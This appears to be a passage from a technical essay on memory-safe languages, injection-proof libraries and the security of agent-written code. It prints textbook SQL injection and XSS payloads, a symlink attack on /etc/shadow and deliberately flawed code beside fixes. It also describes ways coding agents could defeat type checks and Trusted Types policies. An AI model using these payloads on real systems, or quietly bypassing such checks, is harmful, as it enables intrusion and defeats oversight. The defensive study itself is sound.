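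The figure for C and C++ is also historical. C++ written today by the same developers with better tools might have far fewer flaws than the old code, so the fairest comparison would be between Rust and C++ from the same years. Vander Stoep doesn't explain how Google counted the 1,000, and that number is hard to reconcile with the annual totals. At that density, 5 million lines of C and C++ would contain 5,000 flaws, or more than 22 years' worth at the 2019 rate. The figure may include many flaws that Google caught internally and never published.

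Google also did not choose at random which projects to write in Rust. Enthusiastic, careful teams may have adopted it first, which would make Rust look better than it is. But Google also uses Rust for firmware and for code that reads untrusted files, where memory errors are especially dangerous, and that could bias the comparison the other way.

### Why changing only the new code helps

Most of Android's code was still in memory-unsafe languages in 2024, yet its memory-safety flaws had fallen by more than 80% since 2019. Google explains this with a model in which vulnerabilities have a half-life. People keep finding and fixing flaws in existing code, so the number left falls roughly exponentially as the code ages. If the average flaw lasts L years, the share still present after t years is

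e^(−t/L).

Google's simulation uses an average lifetime of L = 2.5 years. With that average, half the flaws are gone after about 1.7 years, and five-year-old code has e² ≈ 7.4 times fewer flaws per line than new code. The five-year reduction is only 3.4 times if we use lifetimes from a large study of open-source software, which corresponds to an average lifetime of about four years.

Suppose a company's C++ developers introduce 100 memory-safety flaws a year, each lasting 2.5 years on average. The number of hidden flaws settles at 100 × 2.5 = 250. The company could rewrite a randomly chosen half of its old code in Rust at once but continue to write new code in C++. Or it could leave all the old code alone and write only new code in Rust. If the Rust code adds no memory-safety flaws, the number remaining is:

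| Years after the change | Rewrite half the old code, keep writing C++ | Keep the old code, write new code in Rust |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 125 | 250 |
| 1 | 166 | 168 |
| 2 | 194 | 112 |
| 5 | 233 | 34 |

The rewrite removes 125 flaws immediately, but new C++ code gradually replaces them with new ones. The other policy is no better at first, but it overtakes the rewrite soon after the first year and never requires the company to change working code.

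Google simulated a gradual move to memory-safe languages, assuming that the codebase doubles every six years and that new development takes ten years to switch. The amount of unsafe code keeps growing for much of that time, but the number of flaws still drops sharply by the end. Android's actual results were better than the simulation's. Google says this may be because it also made the old code safer, so not all of the decline is due to Rust. New code in Java and Kotlin, also memory-safe languages, probably contributed too.

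The number of flaws decays only as people find and fix them, so an abandoned program stays as dangerous as it was. The measured lifetimes also include only flaws that people eventually found. If some flaws stay hidden for decades, old code is riskier than the curve shows.

The same curve can be used to correct roughly for how new Android's Rust code is. After one year, people would have found 1 − e^(−1/2.5), or about 33%, of the flaws. If all 5 million lines were only a year old, the corrected upper limit would be about three times higher, or 3.4 per million lines, which is still about 300 times below the C and C++ figure. If people also found flaws in Rust at a tenth of the usual rate, they would have found only about 4% of them. The upper limit would then be about 28 per million lines, or roughly 35 times below the C and C++ figure. The two flaw rates would be close only if several pessimistic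 assumptions were true at once.

The 2025 memory-safety share may not hold for later years. Android's November 2026 update alone fixed more than 200 vulnerabilities (Arghire, 2026, *Android's November 2026 Updates Patch Over 200 Vulnerabilities*). That is more than the roughly 150 that Google's figures imply for all of 2024, although the two counts may cover different components. If the memory-safety share rises again, the cause could be new searches of old C and C++ code, even if Rust code is as safe as before.

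### A rewrite and its audit

The decay model is also a reason for caution about rewriting old programs. After decades of use, a program may have few flaws left, while its replacement is all new code. The uutils project has taken that risk by rewriting the GNU core utilities in Rust. These are the basic commands on most Linux systems, such as `cp` to copy files and `rm` to delete them. Administrators often run them as root, the account with permission to change almost anything, so a small mistake can have serious consequences.

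In October 2025, Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu, made the Rust versions of most core command-line tools its default. It then hired the security firm Zellic to audit them before its next long-term release. Zellic found 73 issues in the most sensitive tools and 40 in the rest, according to Ubuntu's *An update on rust-coreutils*. Of the 73, seven were critical and 11 were high-severity (Coopersmith 2026, *Security audit of rust-coreutils*). Canonical disclosed 44 CVEs in April 2026.

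The audit found no memory-safety flaws in the Rust versions. GNU's C versions have had several in the past few years, including a buffer overflow in `pwd` and an overwrite of memory in `split`, according to corrode's *Bugs Rust Won't Catch*. Corrode is a Rust consultancy and has an interest in the language's reputation, but it acknowledges that GNU's developers have had 40 years to find such flaws and that an audit can't prove the Rust versions have none. The result is still what one would expect from Rust's rules.

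The 44 flaws varied. Recursive `chmod`, which changes permissions on everything in a folder, has a safeguard against running on the whole system. The safeguard only checked whether the path was `/`, the top folder, so a user could bypass it by typing `/../`, which leads to the same place. The Rust version of `comm`, which compares two files, silently replaced any bytes that weren't valid text. `kill -1` should have required the user to name a process to signal, but it tried to terminate every process the user could see.

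The worst bug was in `chroot`, which runs a command with a chosen folder as its entire file system. The tool entered the folder and then looked up a user's name while it still had root's permissions. That lookup can load program code from the folder, so an attacker who could write there could run code as root. The faulty code was valid Rust, and the fix was to look up the name before entering the folder.

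Many of the 44 were differences from GNU's behavior, as uutils' *Rust Coreutils 0.9.0 Release* points out. These differences can be dangerous because scripts depend on details of the old tools. The project now runs GNU's own tests against its code, which probably helps more with a mistake like the one in `kill` than any language feature would.

### Looking up the same path twice

In the largest group of vulnerabilities, a tool checked or changed something at a path, then used the path again and assumed it still led to the same file. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. Ten of the 44 official descriptions listed in *uutils coreutils CVEs* (Funk, 2026) use that term. Two more describe a related mistake, in which a tool creates a file or folder with loose permissions and tightens them a moment later. Another user can open it in between and keep access afterwards.

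The `install` command, which copies programs into place, had the flaw in roughly this form:

```rust
fs::remove_file(target)?;             // delete the old version
let mut out = File::create(target)?;  // look up the path again
io::copy(&mut source, &mut out)?;
```

Suppose root runs this code to install a program in a folder where an attacker can also write. Just after the first line runs, the attacker puts a symbolic link, a small file that redirects to another path, at `target`. If the link points to `/etc/shadow`, where Linux stores scrambled passwords, the second line empties that file and the third writes the new program into it.

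This is Hardy's confused deputy again. The attacker can't write to `/etc/shadow`, but the tool can, because it uses root's permissions on whatever file the name leads to.

Rust's borrowing rules stop a value from changing while other code relies on it, so the text of the path is guaranteed to stay the same between the two lines. But the file system is outside the program's memory, and other programs can change what the path refers to at any time.

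An open file handle closes the gap. Like a capability, a handle refers to one particular file and carries the right to use it, whatever later happens to the file's name. Consider a privileged tool that should make a file public only if it belongs to the user who asked:

```rust
// Two lookups: the path may lead to a different file the second time.
if fs::metadata(path)?.uid() == user {
    fs::set_permissions(path, public)?;
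}

// One lookup: both steps use the file that was opened.
let file = File::open(path)?;
if file.metadata()?.uid() == user {
    file.set_permissions(public)?;
}
```

In the first version, an attacker can pass the check with their own file and then swap in a link to someone else's. In the second version, a swap before `open` gives the tool a handle to the other person's file, so the ownership check fails. A swap after `open` has no effect, because the tool never uses the path again.

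The `install` tool needed a slightly different repair because its file didn't exist yet. The corrected code uses the `create_new` option, which creates a file and returns a handle to it, but fails if anything already exists at that path, including a link. An attacker could still replace one of the folders along the path. A program can guard against this by opening the parent folder once and creating the file relative to the folder's handle.

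Rust's standard library makes the mistake easy because its most convenient file functions take paths. Corrode points out that C programmers more naturally use handles and set permissions when they create a file, so this flaw is in some ways easier to avoid in C. Funk, who works on the GNU tools, gives the example of `mkfifo`, which creates a channel for passing data between programs. The Rust version gave everyone access, then looked up the path a second time to restrict that access. The GNU version sets the right permissions from the start, and its later call does not follow links.

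The uutils developers responded by changing the interface their tools use. Version 0.9.0 added a shared module, `safe_copy`, that protects copying against such swaps, and added similar protection to recursive operations in `cp`, `mv` and `chmod`. An earlier module already used folder handles this way, but only on Linux. The tools therefore remained vulnerable on macOS, and that omission became one of the 44 CVEs. Ubuntu kept GNU's `cp`, `mv` and `rm` in its April 2026 release because of these flaws. By September the developers had fixed them, and Ubuntu 26.10 moved to a full set of Rust tools (Holwerda, 2026, *Ubuntu 26.10 completes transition to Rust-based coreutils*).

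A safe module protects only the code that uses it, and a programmer or an agent can still call the ordinary path functions. A stricter environment can remove those functions. Under WASI, a WebAssembly program can open files only through handles to folders that the host gives it. The program could still look up a name twice and reach the wrong file within those folders, but a planted link couldn't lead it outside them to `/etc/shadow`. Version 0.9.0 of uutils extended WASI support to several more tools, including `ln` and `dd`, according to heise online's *Rust Coreutils 0.9.0*.

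## Libraries that prevent injection flaws in generated code

Many of the flaws in the Rust file tools came from functions that accept a path as plain text. Database and browser functions that accept text can be more dangerous, because the text may contain code. An injection flaw lets an outsider's data reach a function that runs it as code. Memory safety doesn't prevent this, since a program can use memory correctly and still run an attacker's commands. *Safe Coding* (Kern, 2025) describes how Google uses its libraries to prevent these flaws.

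### One query written three ways

Suppose an online shop looks up orders by the customer's name. A programmer using Go, a language from Google, might build the database query by joining pieces of text:

```go
query := "SELECT item FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'"
rows, err := db.Query(query)
```

If a visitor enters the name `x' OR '1'='1`, the quotation mark after `x` ends the name, and the database reads the rest as part of the condition. Since `'1'='1'` is always true, the query returns everyone's orders.

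A parameterized query sends the name separately:

```go
rows, err := db.Query("SELECT item FROM orders WHERE customer = ?", name)
```

The database now looks for a customer whose name is exactly `x' OR '1'='1` and finds none. This code is safe, but `db.Query` takes its query as an ordinary string, so it would also accept the unsafe version, and the programmer has to remember to use the safe form every time.

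Google's database libraries require a special type, `TrustedSqlString`, instead of a string. With a simplified library of this kind, the two versions look like this:

```go
good := safesql.New("SELECT item FROM orders WHERE customer = ?")
rows, err := safeDB.Query(good, name)     // compiles

bad := safesql.New("SELECT item FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'")
// compile error
```

`New` accepts only text that appears in the program's source code. The Go library enforces this by giving the parameter a private type. Go automatically converts literal text to that type but not string variables, and code outside the library can't convert them explicitly because it can't name the type. The value of `name` is known only at run time, so the compiler rejects any query that includes it. For Java, Google adds a small check to the compiler.

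The type also helps when queries pass through several functions. Suppose `ordersWhere(condition)` pastes its argument into a query. Every caller then has to supply safe text, and so does every function that passes text to those callers. A reviewer would have to trace the text through all these functions. If the parameter is a `TrustedSqlString`, the compiler checks each call, and experts need to study only the library. Kern calls such a library a safe abstraction, meaning its functions are safe however ordinary code calls them.

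The library prevents SQL injection only in code that uses it. A program that can call the ordinary `db.Query` can still contain the flaw, so Google's build tools reject uses of that function outside a list of approved files.

### What the query type guarantees

Let L be the set of all pieces of text in the program's source code. The library can turn any piece in L into a `TrustedSqlString` and can join existing ones. It follows by induction that every query has the form

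l₁ + l₂ + … + lₙ, where each lᵢ is in L.

No query can contain text that came directly from a visitor. The program can still vary its queries, for example by choosing between the fixed endings `ORDER BY date` and `ORDER BY price` when a visitor sorts a list.

But the rule doesn't limit which queries are possible. If L contains every letter and symbol as a separate piece, the program can assemble any text. Kern describes how a determined programmer could exploit this with a function that reads a visitor's text one character at a time, looks up the matching literal and joins the results. The compiler would accept this function, and SQL injection would be possible again.

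Kern reports that this isn't a significant problem at Google, because trusted developers are very unlikely to write code that looks so obviously wrong. He says the method protects well-meaning developers from mistakes and isn't meant for code whose authors may be malicious. Coding agents are a harder case because even an agent with no harmful aim may keep rewriting its code until the compiler errors stop, and a workaround like this one would stop them. An attacker could also use prompt injection to request one. Operators who rely on such a library for agents' code should search for workarounds as well as direct calls to the forbidden functions.

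### The same mistake in a web page

Cross-site scripting (XSS) is an injection flaw that lets an attacker run a script in someone else's browser. Kern's *Securing the Tangled Web* (2014) gives the example of a photo-sharing site that notifies users when someone shares an album with them. The site assigns the message to `innerHTML`, a property whose contents the browser interprets as HTML, the language of web pages:

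```javascript
notice.innerHTML = "You can now view " + albumTitle;
```

A malicious user can name an album `<img src=x onerror="attack()">`. The recipient's browser tries to load the image, fails, and runs the attacker's script. That script can do whatever the recipient can do on the site.

The site can prevent this by escaping the title, which means replacing symbols such as `<` with codes that the browser displays as ordinary characters. But the right treatment depends on where the text goes. Escaping doesn't change the link `javascript:attack()`, and clicking it runs the script, so for links the site has to check that the address starts with something harmless, such as `https`. Reviewers also struggle to tell whether anyone has already made the text safe, because it may have passed through several servers and a database since the attacker typed it.

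Google again addresses this with types. A `SafeHtml` value is safe to display as HTML, a `SafeUrl` is safe to follow as a link, and a `TrustedResourceUrl` is an address from which the page may load scripts. *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Wang, Bangert and Kern, 2021) describes six such types and four ways to create their values. A programmer can use text from the source code, run untrusted text through a sanitizer that removes anything executable, or fill in a template that escapes each value according to its position. If none of these works, the programmer can convert arbitrary text with a special function, but a security expert has to approve each use.

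Google's compilers reject direct assignments to `innerHTML` and similar properties, and the library offers replacements that accept only the safe types. These types also let code in one part of a system rely on checks made in another. For example, users of the photo site may want bold text in their profiles, which escaping would prevent. The server can sanitize the profile once and store the result as `SafeHtml`, and later code can display it without checking it again.

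The compile-time check has gaps because the type systems of JavaScript and its typed variant, TypeScript, are unsound. A programmer can cast an object to a different type and then assign a dangerous link to it without an error. Google relies on code reviewers to notice such casts. TACIT's safe mode forbids this kind of cast in agents' Scala code.

### Moving the check into the browser

Trusted Types, a browser feature that grew out of Google's work, makes a similar check while the page runs. A developer writes a policy, which is a set of functions that turn strings into trusted values. This policy uses DOMPurify, a widely used sanitizer:

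```javascript
const policy = trustedTypes.createPolicy("clean", {
  createHTML: text => DOMPurify.sanitize(text),
});
notice.innerHTML = policy.createHTML(albumTitle);  // allowed
notice.innerHTML = albumTitle;                     // error
```

The last line causes an error only if the website sends a setting called `require-trusted-types-for` with the page. Without that setting, trusted values are optional. A second setting lists the names of the policies the page may create. According to MDN's *Trusted Types API*, the feature has worked in the latest version of every major browser since February 2026.

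A run-time check can catch a dangerous assignment that the compiler missed, but it may also break part of a page for users if developers never tested that part with the check on. Browsers therefore offer a mode that reports violations without blocking them. Adopting Trusted Types can also expose old mistakes. Wang, Guðmundsson and Kotowicz discovered a previously unknown vulnerability in Angular, a popular web framework, while adapting it (*Adopting Trusted Types in Production Web Frameworks to Prevent DOM-Based Cross-Site Scripting*, 2021).

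They also point out that the browser doesn't check whether a policy makes strings safe. A policy named `default` applies automatically to strings that no other policy has handled. If its function returns every string unchanged, all the errors disappear and the page is as vulnerable as before. A coding agent that has to clear a long list of Trusted Types errors could do it this way in three lines. To prevent this, an operator can keep the policies and the website's settings in files that the agent can't edit.

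A newer browser function, `setHTML`, sanitizes text before adding it to the page, so ordinary cases don't need a custom policy. Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026) notes that a site can combine it with strict Trusted Types settings that allow `setHTML` but block the unsafe alternatives. This is better for an agent than a custom policy because the agent doesn't have to write a sanitizing function, which it could get wrong.

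### Google's results

Google has published before-and-after counts of XSS bugs for three of its applications. The first two rows, from the 2014 article, cover all XSS bugs. The third, from Wang and colleagues, covers only XSS in code that runs in the browser.

| Application | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Large application with over 1,000 templates | 31 in 2012 | 4 in the year to mid-2014 |
| Second large application, still switching | 21 | 9 |
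| One actively developed product | 10 in the year before adoption | 1 in the year after |

Kern calls the early figures anecdotal, since bug counts also depend on the size of the code and the training of its developers. Chance is an unlikely explanation for the drop in the third case. If each of the 11 flaws had been equally likely to fall in either year, the probability of at most one falling in the later year would be 12/2¹¹, or about 0.6%. But this team was among the pioneers of the method and may have been unusually careful. Teams may also be more likely to adopt a new defense after a bad year, when the number of flaws would probably have dropped somewhat anyway.

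The company-wide data are stronger evidence. Google began to require the compile-time checks for all its JavaScript in early 2018, but exempted existing violations so that old code would still compile. Over about the next two years, browser-side XSS fell as a share of the serious flaws that outsiders reported. A growing share of the remaining XSS flaws was in exempted code, even though the amount of such code was falling. A defense that protected old and new code equally would not have produced this pattern, so the checks probably account for much of the decline.

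By 2025, hundreds of complex applications built on Google's hardened frameworks together averaged less than one XSS report a year, according to Kern. Google Photos, which used these frameworks from the start, had never had one. Hundreds of applications that use the hardened database libraries had gone more than a decade without a reported SQL injection flaw. These are Google's own figures, and they count only reported flaws, so others may remain undiscovered. However, Google pays outsiders for such reports and had spent millions of dollars on XSS reports by 2021, so people had good reason to look for flaws.

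Developers rarely needed exemptions from the method. Wang and colleagues counted fewer than eight requests a week between October 2018 and February 2019, when Google's developers were making about 10,000 changes to JavaScript files a week. Fewer than one change in 1,000 therefore needed a security review. Experts approved some requests immediately, asked for changes to others, and rejected those for which a safe function would work. By the end of 2020, exemptions covered less than 1% of more than a million JavaScript files, though that could still mean thousands of files, most of them old.

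Google was also unusually well suited to this approach. Nearly all its code is in one repository, every change needs a review, and everyone uses the same build tools, so a small team of experts could maintain the libraries and checks for thousands of developers. A company with many separate codebases and no security team would find this harder, though it could still use the libraries and checkers that Google has open-sourced.

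### Why injection flaws are still common

XSS and SQL injection rank first and second in the *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), an annual list from MITRE, a US non-profit that catalogues software weaknesses. MITRE compiled the list from 39,080 publicly reported vulnerabilities, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses of 2025 Revealed* (2025). Both flaws have been on the list since 2009, and parameterized queries and escaping have been standard advice for at least as long.

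The ranking partly reflects how MITRE groups flaws. All kinds of XSS share one entry, for example, while memory errors are spread over several, including use-after-free in eighth place. A high rank also doesn't mean that attackers exploit a flaw most often. MITRE links only seven XSS vulnerabilities and four SQL injection vulnerabilities to the US government's catalogue of exploited flaws. As Joe (2025) noted in a mailing-list discussion, it links 20 vulnerabilities for operating-system command injection, in which a program pastes an outsider's text into a system command.

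Even so, these flaws are plainly still common, and the main reason is probably that most libraries offer the safe method as an option. Go's standard database function accepts both versions of the shop's query, and browsers still let pages assign plain strings to `innerHTML` unless the site forbids it. Kern estimates that a large web application has hundreds or thousands of places where data could cause XSS. Suppose that there are 1,000 such places and that developers handle each one correctly with probability 99.9%. The chance that the whole application is free of the flaw is then only

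0.999¹⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 37%.

Better training might raise the 99.9%, but the number of places where developers must choose the safe option grows with the application. A library with no unsafe option removes that choice, so developers can introduce the flaw only through an approved exception, a workaround, or a bug in the library itself.

The people who maintain languages, frameworks and build tools have to make such a change, and they have reason to hesitate because removing an old function breaks existing programs. Zorz (2026) reports in *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* that CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, has urged software makers to do this work instead of leaving customers to defend themselves.

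### How secure is the code that agents write?

Agents learn from public code, where unsafe queries and assignments are common, so they may repeat human mistakes. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2025) tested this in *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* with SusVibes, a benchmark of 186 requests for new features in real open-source projects. Human programmers had originally introduced a vulnerability when implementing each feature. All 12 combinations of agents and models tested performed poorly on security.

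SWE-Agent with Claude 4 Sonnet produced working code for 57% of the tasks (about 106) but secure code for only 11.8% (about 22). If the secure solutions also worked, roughly four out of five working solutions contained a vulnerability but would have passed an ordinary test of the feature.

These rates don't apply to software in general, because the researchers chose tasks on which people had already made a security mistake. They are also out of date, since Claude 4 Sonnet is a 2025 model and the best models of late 2026 are far more capable programmers. The newer models' code may not be much more secure, though, because a model can get better at making features work without getting better at making them secure.

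Zhao and colleagues also tried requests that included hints about possible vulnerabilities, but this didn't solve the problem. Like a warning to a human developer, a hint leaves every unsafe function available and relies on the agent to avoid them all. The result therefore gives some support to removing those functions, although it doesn't show that removal would work.

The design of *BaxBench* (2025), another benchmark, suits this question better. Models build the server side of 28 applications in each of 14 frameworks, for a total of 392 tasks in six programming languages. The researchers run each application in an isolated container, test whether it works, and attack it with prepared exploits. Because every application is built in every framework, readers can compare how often the same model introduces the same flaw with different libraries. For a given model, applications built in a framework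 that escapes text by default should have fewer XSS flaws than those built in one that doesn't.

### Which flaws a safer library would exclude

Libraries can prevent some of the four highest-ranked weaknesses on MITRE's list better than others. Cross-site request forgery, ranked third, lets a malicious website make a visitor's browser send an unwanted request to a site where the visitor is logged in. Missing authorization, which rose from ninth to fourth, means that a program doesn't check whether a user is allowed to do what they request.

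| Flaw | What a library or framework can require | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Cross-site scripting | A safe type for all HTML and links | A faulty sanitizer or a careless policy |
| SQL injection | A query type that accepts only text from the source code | A workaround or a bad exemption |
| Cross-site request forgery | A secret code in every request that changes data | A change that the framework mistakes for a harmless read |
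| Missing authorization | Access to data only through an object for the current user | A wrong rule about who may see what |
| Flawed business logic | Very little that applies to every program | Almost anything |

The shop's order page shows why a safe query type isn't enough. Suppose an agent writes this function to display one order:

```go
func showOrder(user User, id int) (*sql.Rows, error) {
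    query := safesql.New("SELECT item FROM orders WHERE id = ?")
    return safeDB.Query(query, id)
}
```

This code has no SQL injection flaw, but any logged-in customer can read anyone's order by changing the order number, because the function never uses its `user` argument. The type checker doesn't reject the code, since the same code might be correct on an administrator's page.

A stricter library could exclude this mistake too. Instead of `safeDB`, the framework could give the agent's code an `orders` object already bound to the current customer. Its `get(id)` method would always add `AND customer_id = ?` to the query and fill in the customer's number, so the agent could not omit the check. The `reply` function that can write to only one person works the same way. Somebody would have to decide in advance what customers may see, and the shop would need a different object for its administrators.

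Business logic is much harder to protect with libraries. An agent may write a program that lets customers use the same discount code twice, even though its queries are safe and its authorization is correct. A library could enforce a rule that each code works once, but only after someone has thought of the rule, and another shop may want codes that work every week. To avoid such flaws, developers still depend on tests, review and the quality of the model.

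### What changes when agents use hardened libraries

The type checker treats code the same whether a person or an agent wrote it. So if an agent's program compiles against Google's database library without workarounds or exemptions, it is as free of SQL injection as a human developer's would be. This part of Google's experience should carry over to agents, including weak ones.

The low number of exemptions at Google may not carry over to AI agents. Google's developers could ask colleagues for help, and many had used the libraries for years. An agent that doesn't know a library may ask for an exemption when a safe function would work. Even if agents needed exemptions at the same rate as Google's developers, a tenfold increase in code changes would raise the number of requests from eight a week to 80. A company might then be tempted to let another model approve them, which would make the guarantee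 depend on a model's judgment again.

Error messages could reduce unnecessary requests. When Google's tools reject an unsafe function, they point developers to the safe one and often propose the corrected code. An agent could apply that correction on its next attempt.

A direct experiment would give the same model the same tasks twice, once with ordinary libraries and once with a build that rejects the unsafe functions. Researchers would count injection flaws, completed tasks, requests for exemptions and attempts to get around the rules. They would also need to count authorization and logic flaws, because an agent that spends its effort satisfying the type checker could conceivably make more mistakes elsewhere.

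## What happens when agents write Rust

Like the type checks in Google's libraries, Rust's checks don't depend on who wrote the code, but agents can avoid some of them by using `unsafe` blocks. When the compiler rejects a program, an agent can restructure it so that each value lives long enough, or it can switch to raw pointers inside an `unsafe` block. Both remove the error, and the second is often less work. How much of Rust's memory safety guarantee remains therefore depends on how often agents choose the second option and how well they write the unsafe code.

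### Porting Bun in 11 days

In May 2026, Jarred Sumner used agents to translate Bun, a program that runs JavaScript outside the browser, from Zig to Rust. In Zig, as in C, programmers manage memory themselves. Bun's developers kept having to fix use-after-free and double-free errors, even though they ran a memory checker on every change and fuzzed Bun around the clock. Sumner describes the port in *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (2026). He works for Anthropic, which bought Bun in December 2025 and makes the model he used, a pre-release version of Claude Fable 5, so he has an interest in presenting the port as a success.

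Sumner first spent about three hours with Claude on a guide that matched Zig patterns to Rust ones. Agents then examined every field of every data structure, worked out how long its data had to stay valid, and recorded the answers for the agents that would write the code. After a trial on three files, they translated all 1,448, with about 64 instances of Claude running at peak. For each piece of work, one instance wrote the code and at least two others reviewed it for mistakes. The reviewers saw only the changes and had instructions to assume the code was wrong.

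The port took 11 days, added just over a million lines and would have cost about $165,000 at Anthropic's public prices. Sumner read a lot of the code himself, but nobody could have read all of it in that time, so he relied heavily on Bun's existing tests. In *Rewriting Bun in Rust*, a comment on Sumner's post, Willison (2026) points out that this was possible because Bun's developers had written the tests in TypeScript, so they could check either version. On Linux, the tests make nearly 1.4 million checks. Sumner merged the port when every test passed on all six platforms, with none skipped or deleted.

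By 8 July, Sumner had counted 128 bugs in the last Zig version that didn't occur in the Rust version. He also knew of 19 regressions from the port, all of which his team had fixed. The difference between these counts doesn't measure the benefit of Rust, because the 128 bugs range from miscolored help text to crashes, and the team also improved its leak-detection tools during the same period. The 19 regressions are only the ones people had noticed, and most users didn't have the Rust version yet, although Anthropic's Claude Code had run on it since June.

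Most regressions came from code that looks the same in both languages but behaves differently. Zig's `assert(f())` always calls `f`, but Rust's release builds omit `debug_assert!(f())`, including the call to `f`. In one place, `f` registered a file for live reloading, so reloading broke for some users but worked in the developers' own builds. Rust's rules can't catch this mistake because it doesn't involve memory.

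In another case Rust limited the damage. An agent left a placeholder in the code that made a table too small. This exposed an error copied from the Zig version that made Bun write one position past the end of a list. Bun's developers had compiled the Zig version for macOS and Linux without bounds checks, so the same write would have corrupted memory in those builds. The Rust version stopped with an error message instead.

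### A use-after-free that compiled

The reviewing agents caught a more serious mistake before the merge. Bun exchanges data with programs it starts through pipes, and on Windows it closes them with libuv, a C library. Sumner's condensed version of the ported code includes these lines:

```rust
StdioResult::Buffer(mut pipe) => {
    pipe.close(Subprocess::on_pipe_close)
}
```

The variable `pipe` owns its memory, so Rust frees it at the closing brace. But libuv keeps a pointer to that memory until its next round of work, when it finishes closing the pipe and calls `on_pipe_close`, which frees the memory again. This causes a use-after-free and then a double free. The agents fixed it by writing `Box::leak(pipe).close(...)`, which stops Rust from freeing the memory, so only `on_pipe_close` frees it.

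The faulty lines, as Sumner shows them, contain no `unsafe` keyword. The unsafe call is presumably inside `close`, and the fix implies that `close` only borrows the pipe, even though libuv goes on using it afterwards. A better wrapper would take ownership:

```rust
fn close(&mut self, done: Callback)        // the caller still frees the pipe
fn close(self: Box<Self>, done: Callback)  // the caller gives the pipe away
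```

The agent's original lines would have been correct if the wrapper had used the second signature and its body had passed the memory on to libuv. The compiler would also have rejected any later use of `pipe`. A better wrapper would have protected every call, not just the one that the published fix repairs.

### Why 4% can mean different risks

On 8 July, about 27,000 of Bun's 780,000 lines of Rust (3.5%, which Sumner gives as "about 4%") were in unsafe blocks, a share similar to Android's. At Android's rate of one known flaw in roughly 200,000 unsafe lines, Bun's unsafe code would contain 27,000 / 200,000 ≈ 0.14 flaws, or probably none, but this estimate is almost certainly too low.

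One reason is that the port keeps designs from Zig, which has no ownership rules. Sumner wanted Rust that looked like a direct translation of the Zig code so that his team could still understand it, and planned to make it more idiomatic later. Much of Android's Rust was new, so its developers could choose designs that suited the compiler from the start. They also wrote their code over several years, with human review.

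How the unsafe code is spread out also matters. Bun uses the `unsafe` keyword about 13,000 times, an average of once every 60 lines, and 78% of the blocks are a single line, such as a call to a C library. Even a one-line block can be hard to check. Closing a pipe, for example, is safe only if the pipe's memory outlives the call, which depends on ordinary code elsewhere. Someone who reviewed only Bun's 27,000 unsafe lines could have missed the pipe mistake. If `close` had taken ownership of the pipe, reviewing the wrapper would have been enough.

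Bun's team now tests a growing part of the code with Miri, a tool that interprets Rust programs and reports undefined behavior. Miri finds only problems that the tests trigger, and it generally can't run C code, which many of Bun's unsafe blocks call. The team has also completed 11 rounds of security review by Claude and fuzzes Bun's parsers continuously.

Sumner expects the unsafe share to fall as the team refactors the code, but a lower share wouldn't prove that Bun had become safer. If a program reads kernel memory ten times, an agent can write ten unsafe calls, or put one in a small wrapper function and call that function ten times. *HEIMDALL* (Dasu, Santra and colleagues, 2026) found that GPT-5.4 tended to use wrappers. Its programs averaged 6 to 10 unsafe operations, compared with 18 to 30 for the other models. Moving an unsafe call into a wrapper doesn't by itself change what the program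 does when it runs, so it makes the code safer only if the wrapper also prevents misuse.

### Contest puzzles and kernel programs

Controlled studies disagree about how readily models use escape hatches. In *AdaTrans*, Liu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) had gpt-4o-mini, a small model from 2024, translate 104 C solutions to programming-contest puzzles. Only 1.19% of the translations that passed all the tests contained an unsafe block, which amounts to one program in each of three runs. The low rate probably isn't due to their system, which answers each compiler error with advice for that kind of error. Liu and colleagues credit the system, but the same model's rate was 1.05% without it.

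Dasu and colleagues studied eBPF programs, which run inside the Linux kernel to inspect network traffic or record what the system is doing. Four coding agents each translated 51 of these programs from C to Rust with Aya, a library that provides typed functions for writing eBPF programs. All the translations compiled, but only 35% to 45% of each agent's translations passed a check that they didn't bypass Aya's typed functions. Dasu and colleagues write that models "reach for" code that bypasses these functions "by default".

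In 73% of the safety failures across the study, the model had declared a fixed setting, such as which process to watch, as a changeable global variable and read it with a raw memory operation. The program might then ignore the user's setting, or other software might change it, but this doesn't mean that more than half of the programs could corrupt memory. More seriously, a few translations read a fixed number of bytes where the text was usually shorter and ignored any error, which was how the C originals had leaked memory.

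The difference between the studies probably comes mostly from the tasks. A contest solution reads text, computes an answer and prints it, and Rust's standard library has safe functions for all of that. A kernel program has to call kernel functions and read memory that Rust doesn't manage, so it needs some unsafe operations. Even the translations that Dasu and colleagues proved equivalent to their originals contain 15.5 unsafe operations on average. Bun is closer to the kernel programs because about 20% of its code is C++ and it depends on several C and C++ libraries.

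In both studies, models also copied unsafe designs from the original program. The one recurring unsafe program in the puzzle study came from C code with changeable global tables. The model reproduced these as `static mut`, a kind of global variable that needs unsafe code. The same construct caused most of the safety failures in the kernel study. Any close translation, including Bun's, carries this risk.

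Model ability is a poor explanation because the weakest model wrote the least unsafe code, though neither study gave the same model both tasks. *LLM4C2Rust* (Bedell, Siavash and Moin, 2026) tested a task between those two. Older OpenAI models translated seven command-line tools, such as `cat` and `tail`, and several of the translations contained no raw-pointer dereferences. These tools need access to files, but Rust has safe functions for that, so the result fits the earlier explanation.

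The 1.19% in the puzzle study is a share of programs, while Bun's 3.5% is a share of lines. Less than 0.1% of the lines in the puzzle study were in unsafe blocks, so Bun's share is at least 35 times as high.

### Compiler errors as feedback

An agent doesn't need to know all of Rust's rules in advance, because the compiler reports each violation along with its location and often a suggested fix. When Sumner's agents finished their first draft of Bun and split it into separate parts, the compiler reported about 16,000 errors. A script sorted them by file and divided them among 64 instances of Claude. According to Gergely's *What can we learn from Bun’s rapid Rust rewrite with AI?*, the agents worked through them from midnight to 11:30 a.m., partly while the team slept.

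Liu and colleagues give an example of an error that needs more than a local fix. A program reads words in a loop and stores a reference to each one in a list, but the word's memory is freed at the end of each iteration. The compiler reports that the word "does not live long enough". The right solution is to make the list own its words, using `Vec<String>` instead of `Vec<&str>`. Models often changed unrelated lines first, then silenced the error with unsafe code or by never freeing the memory.

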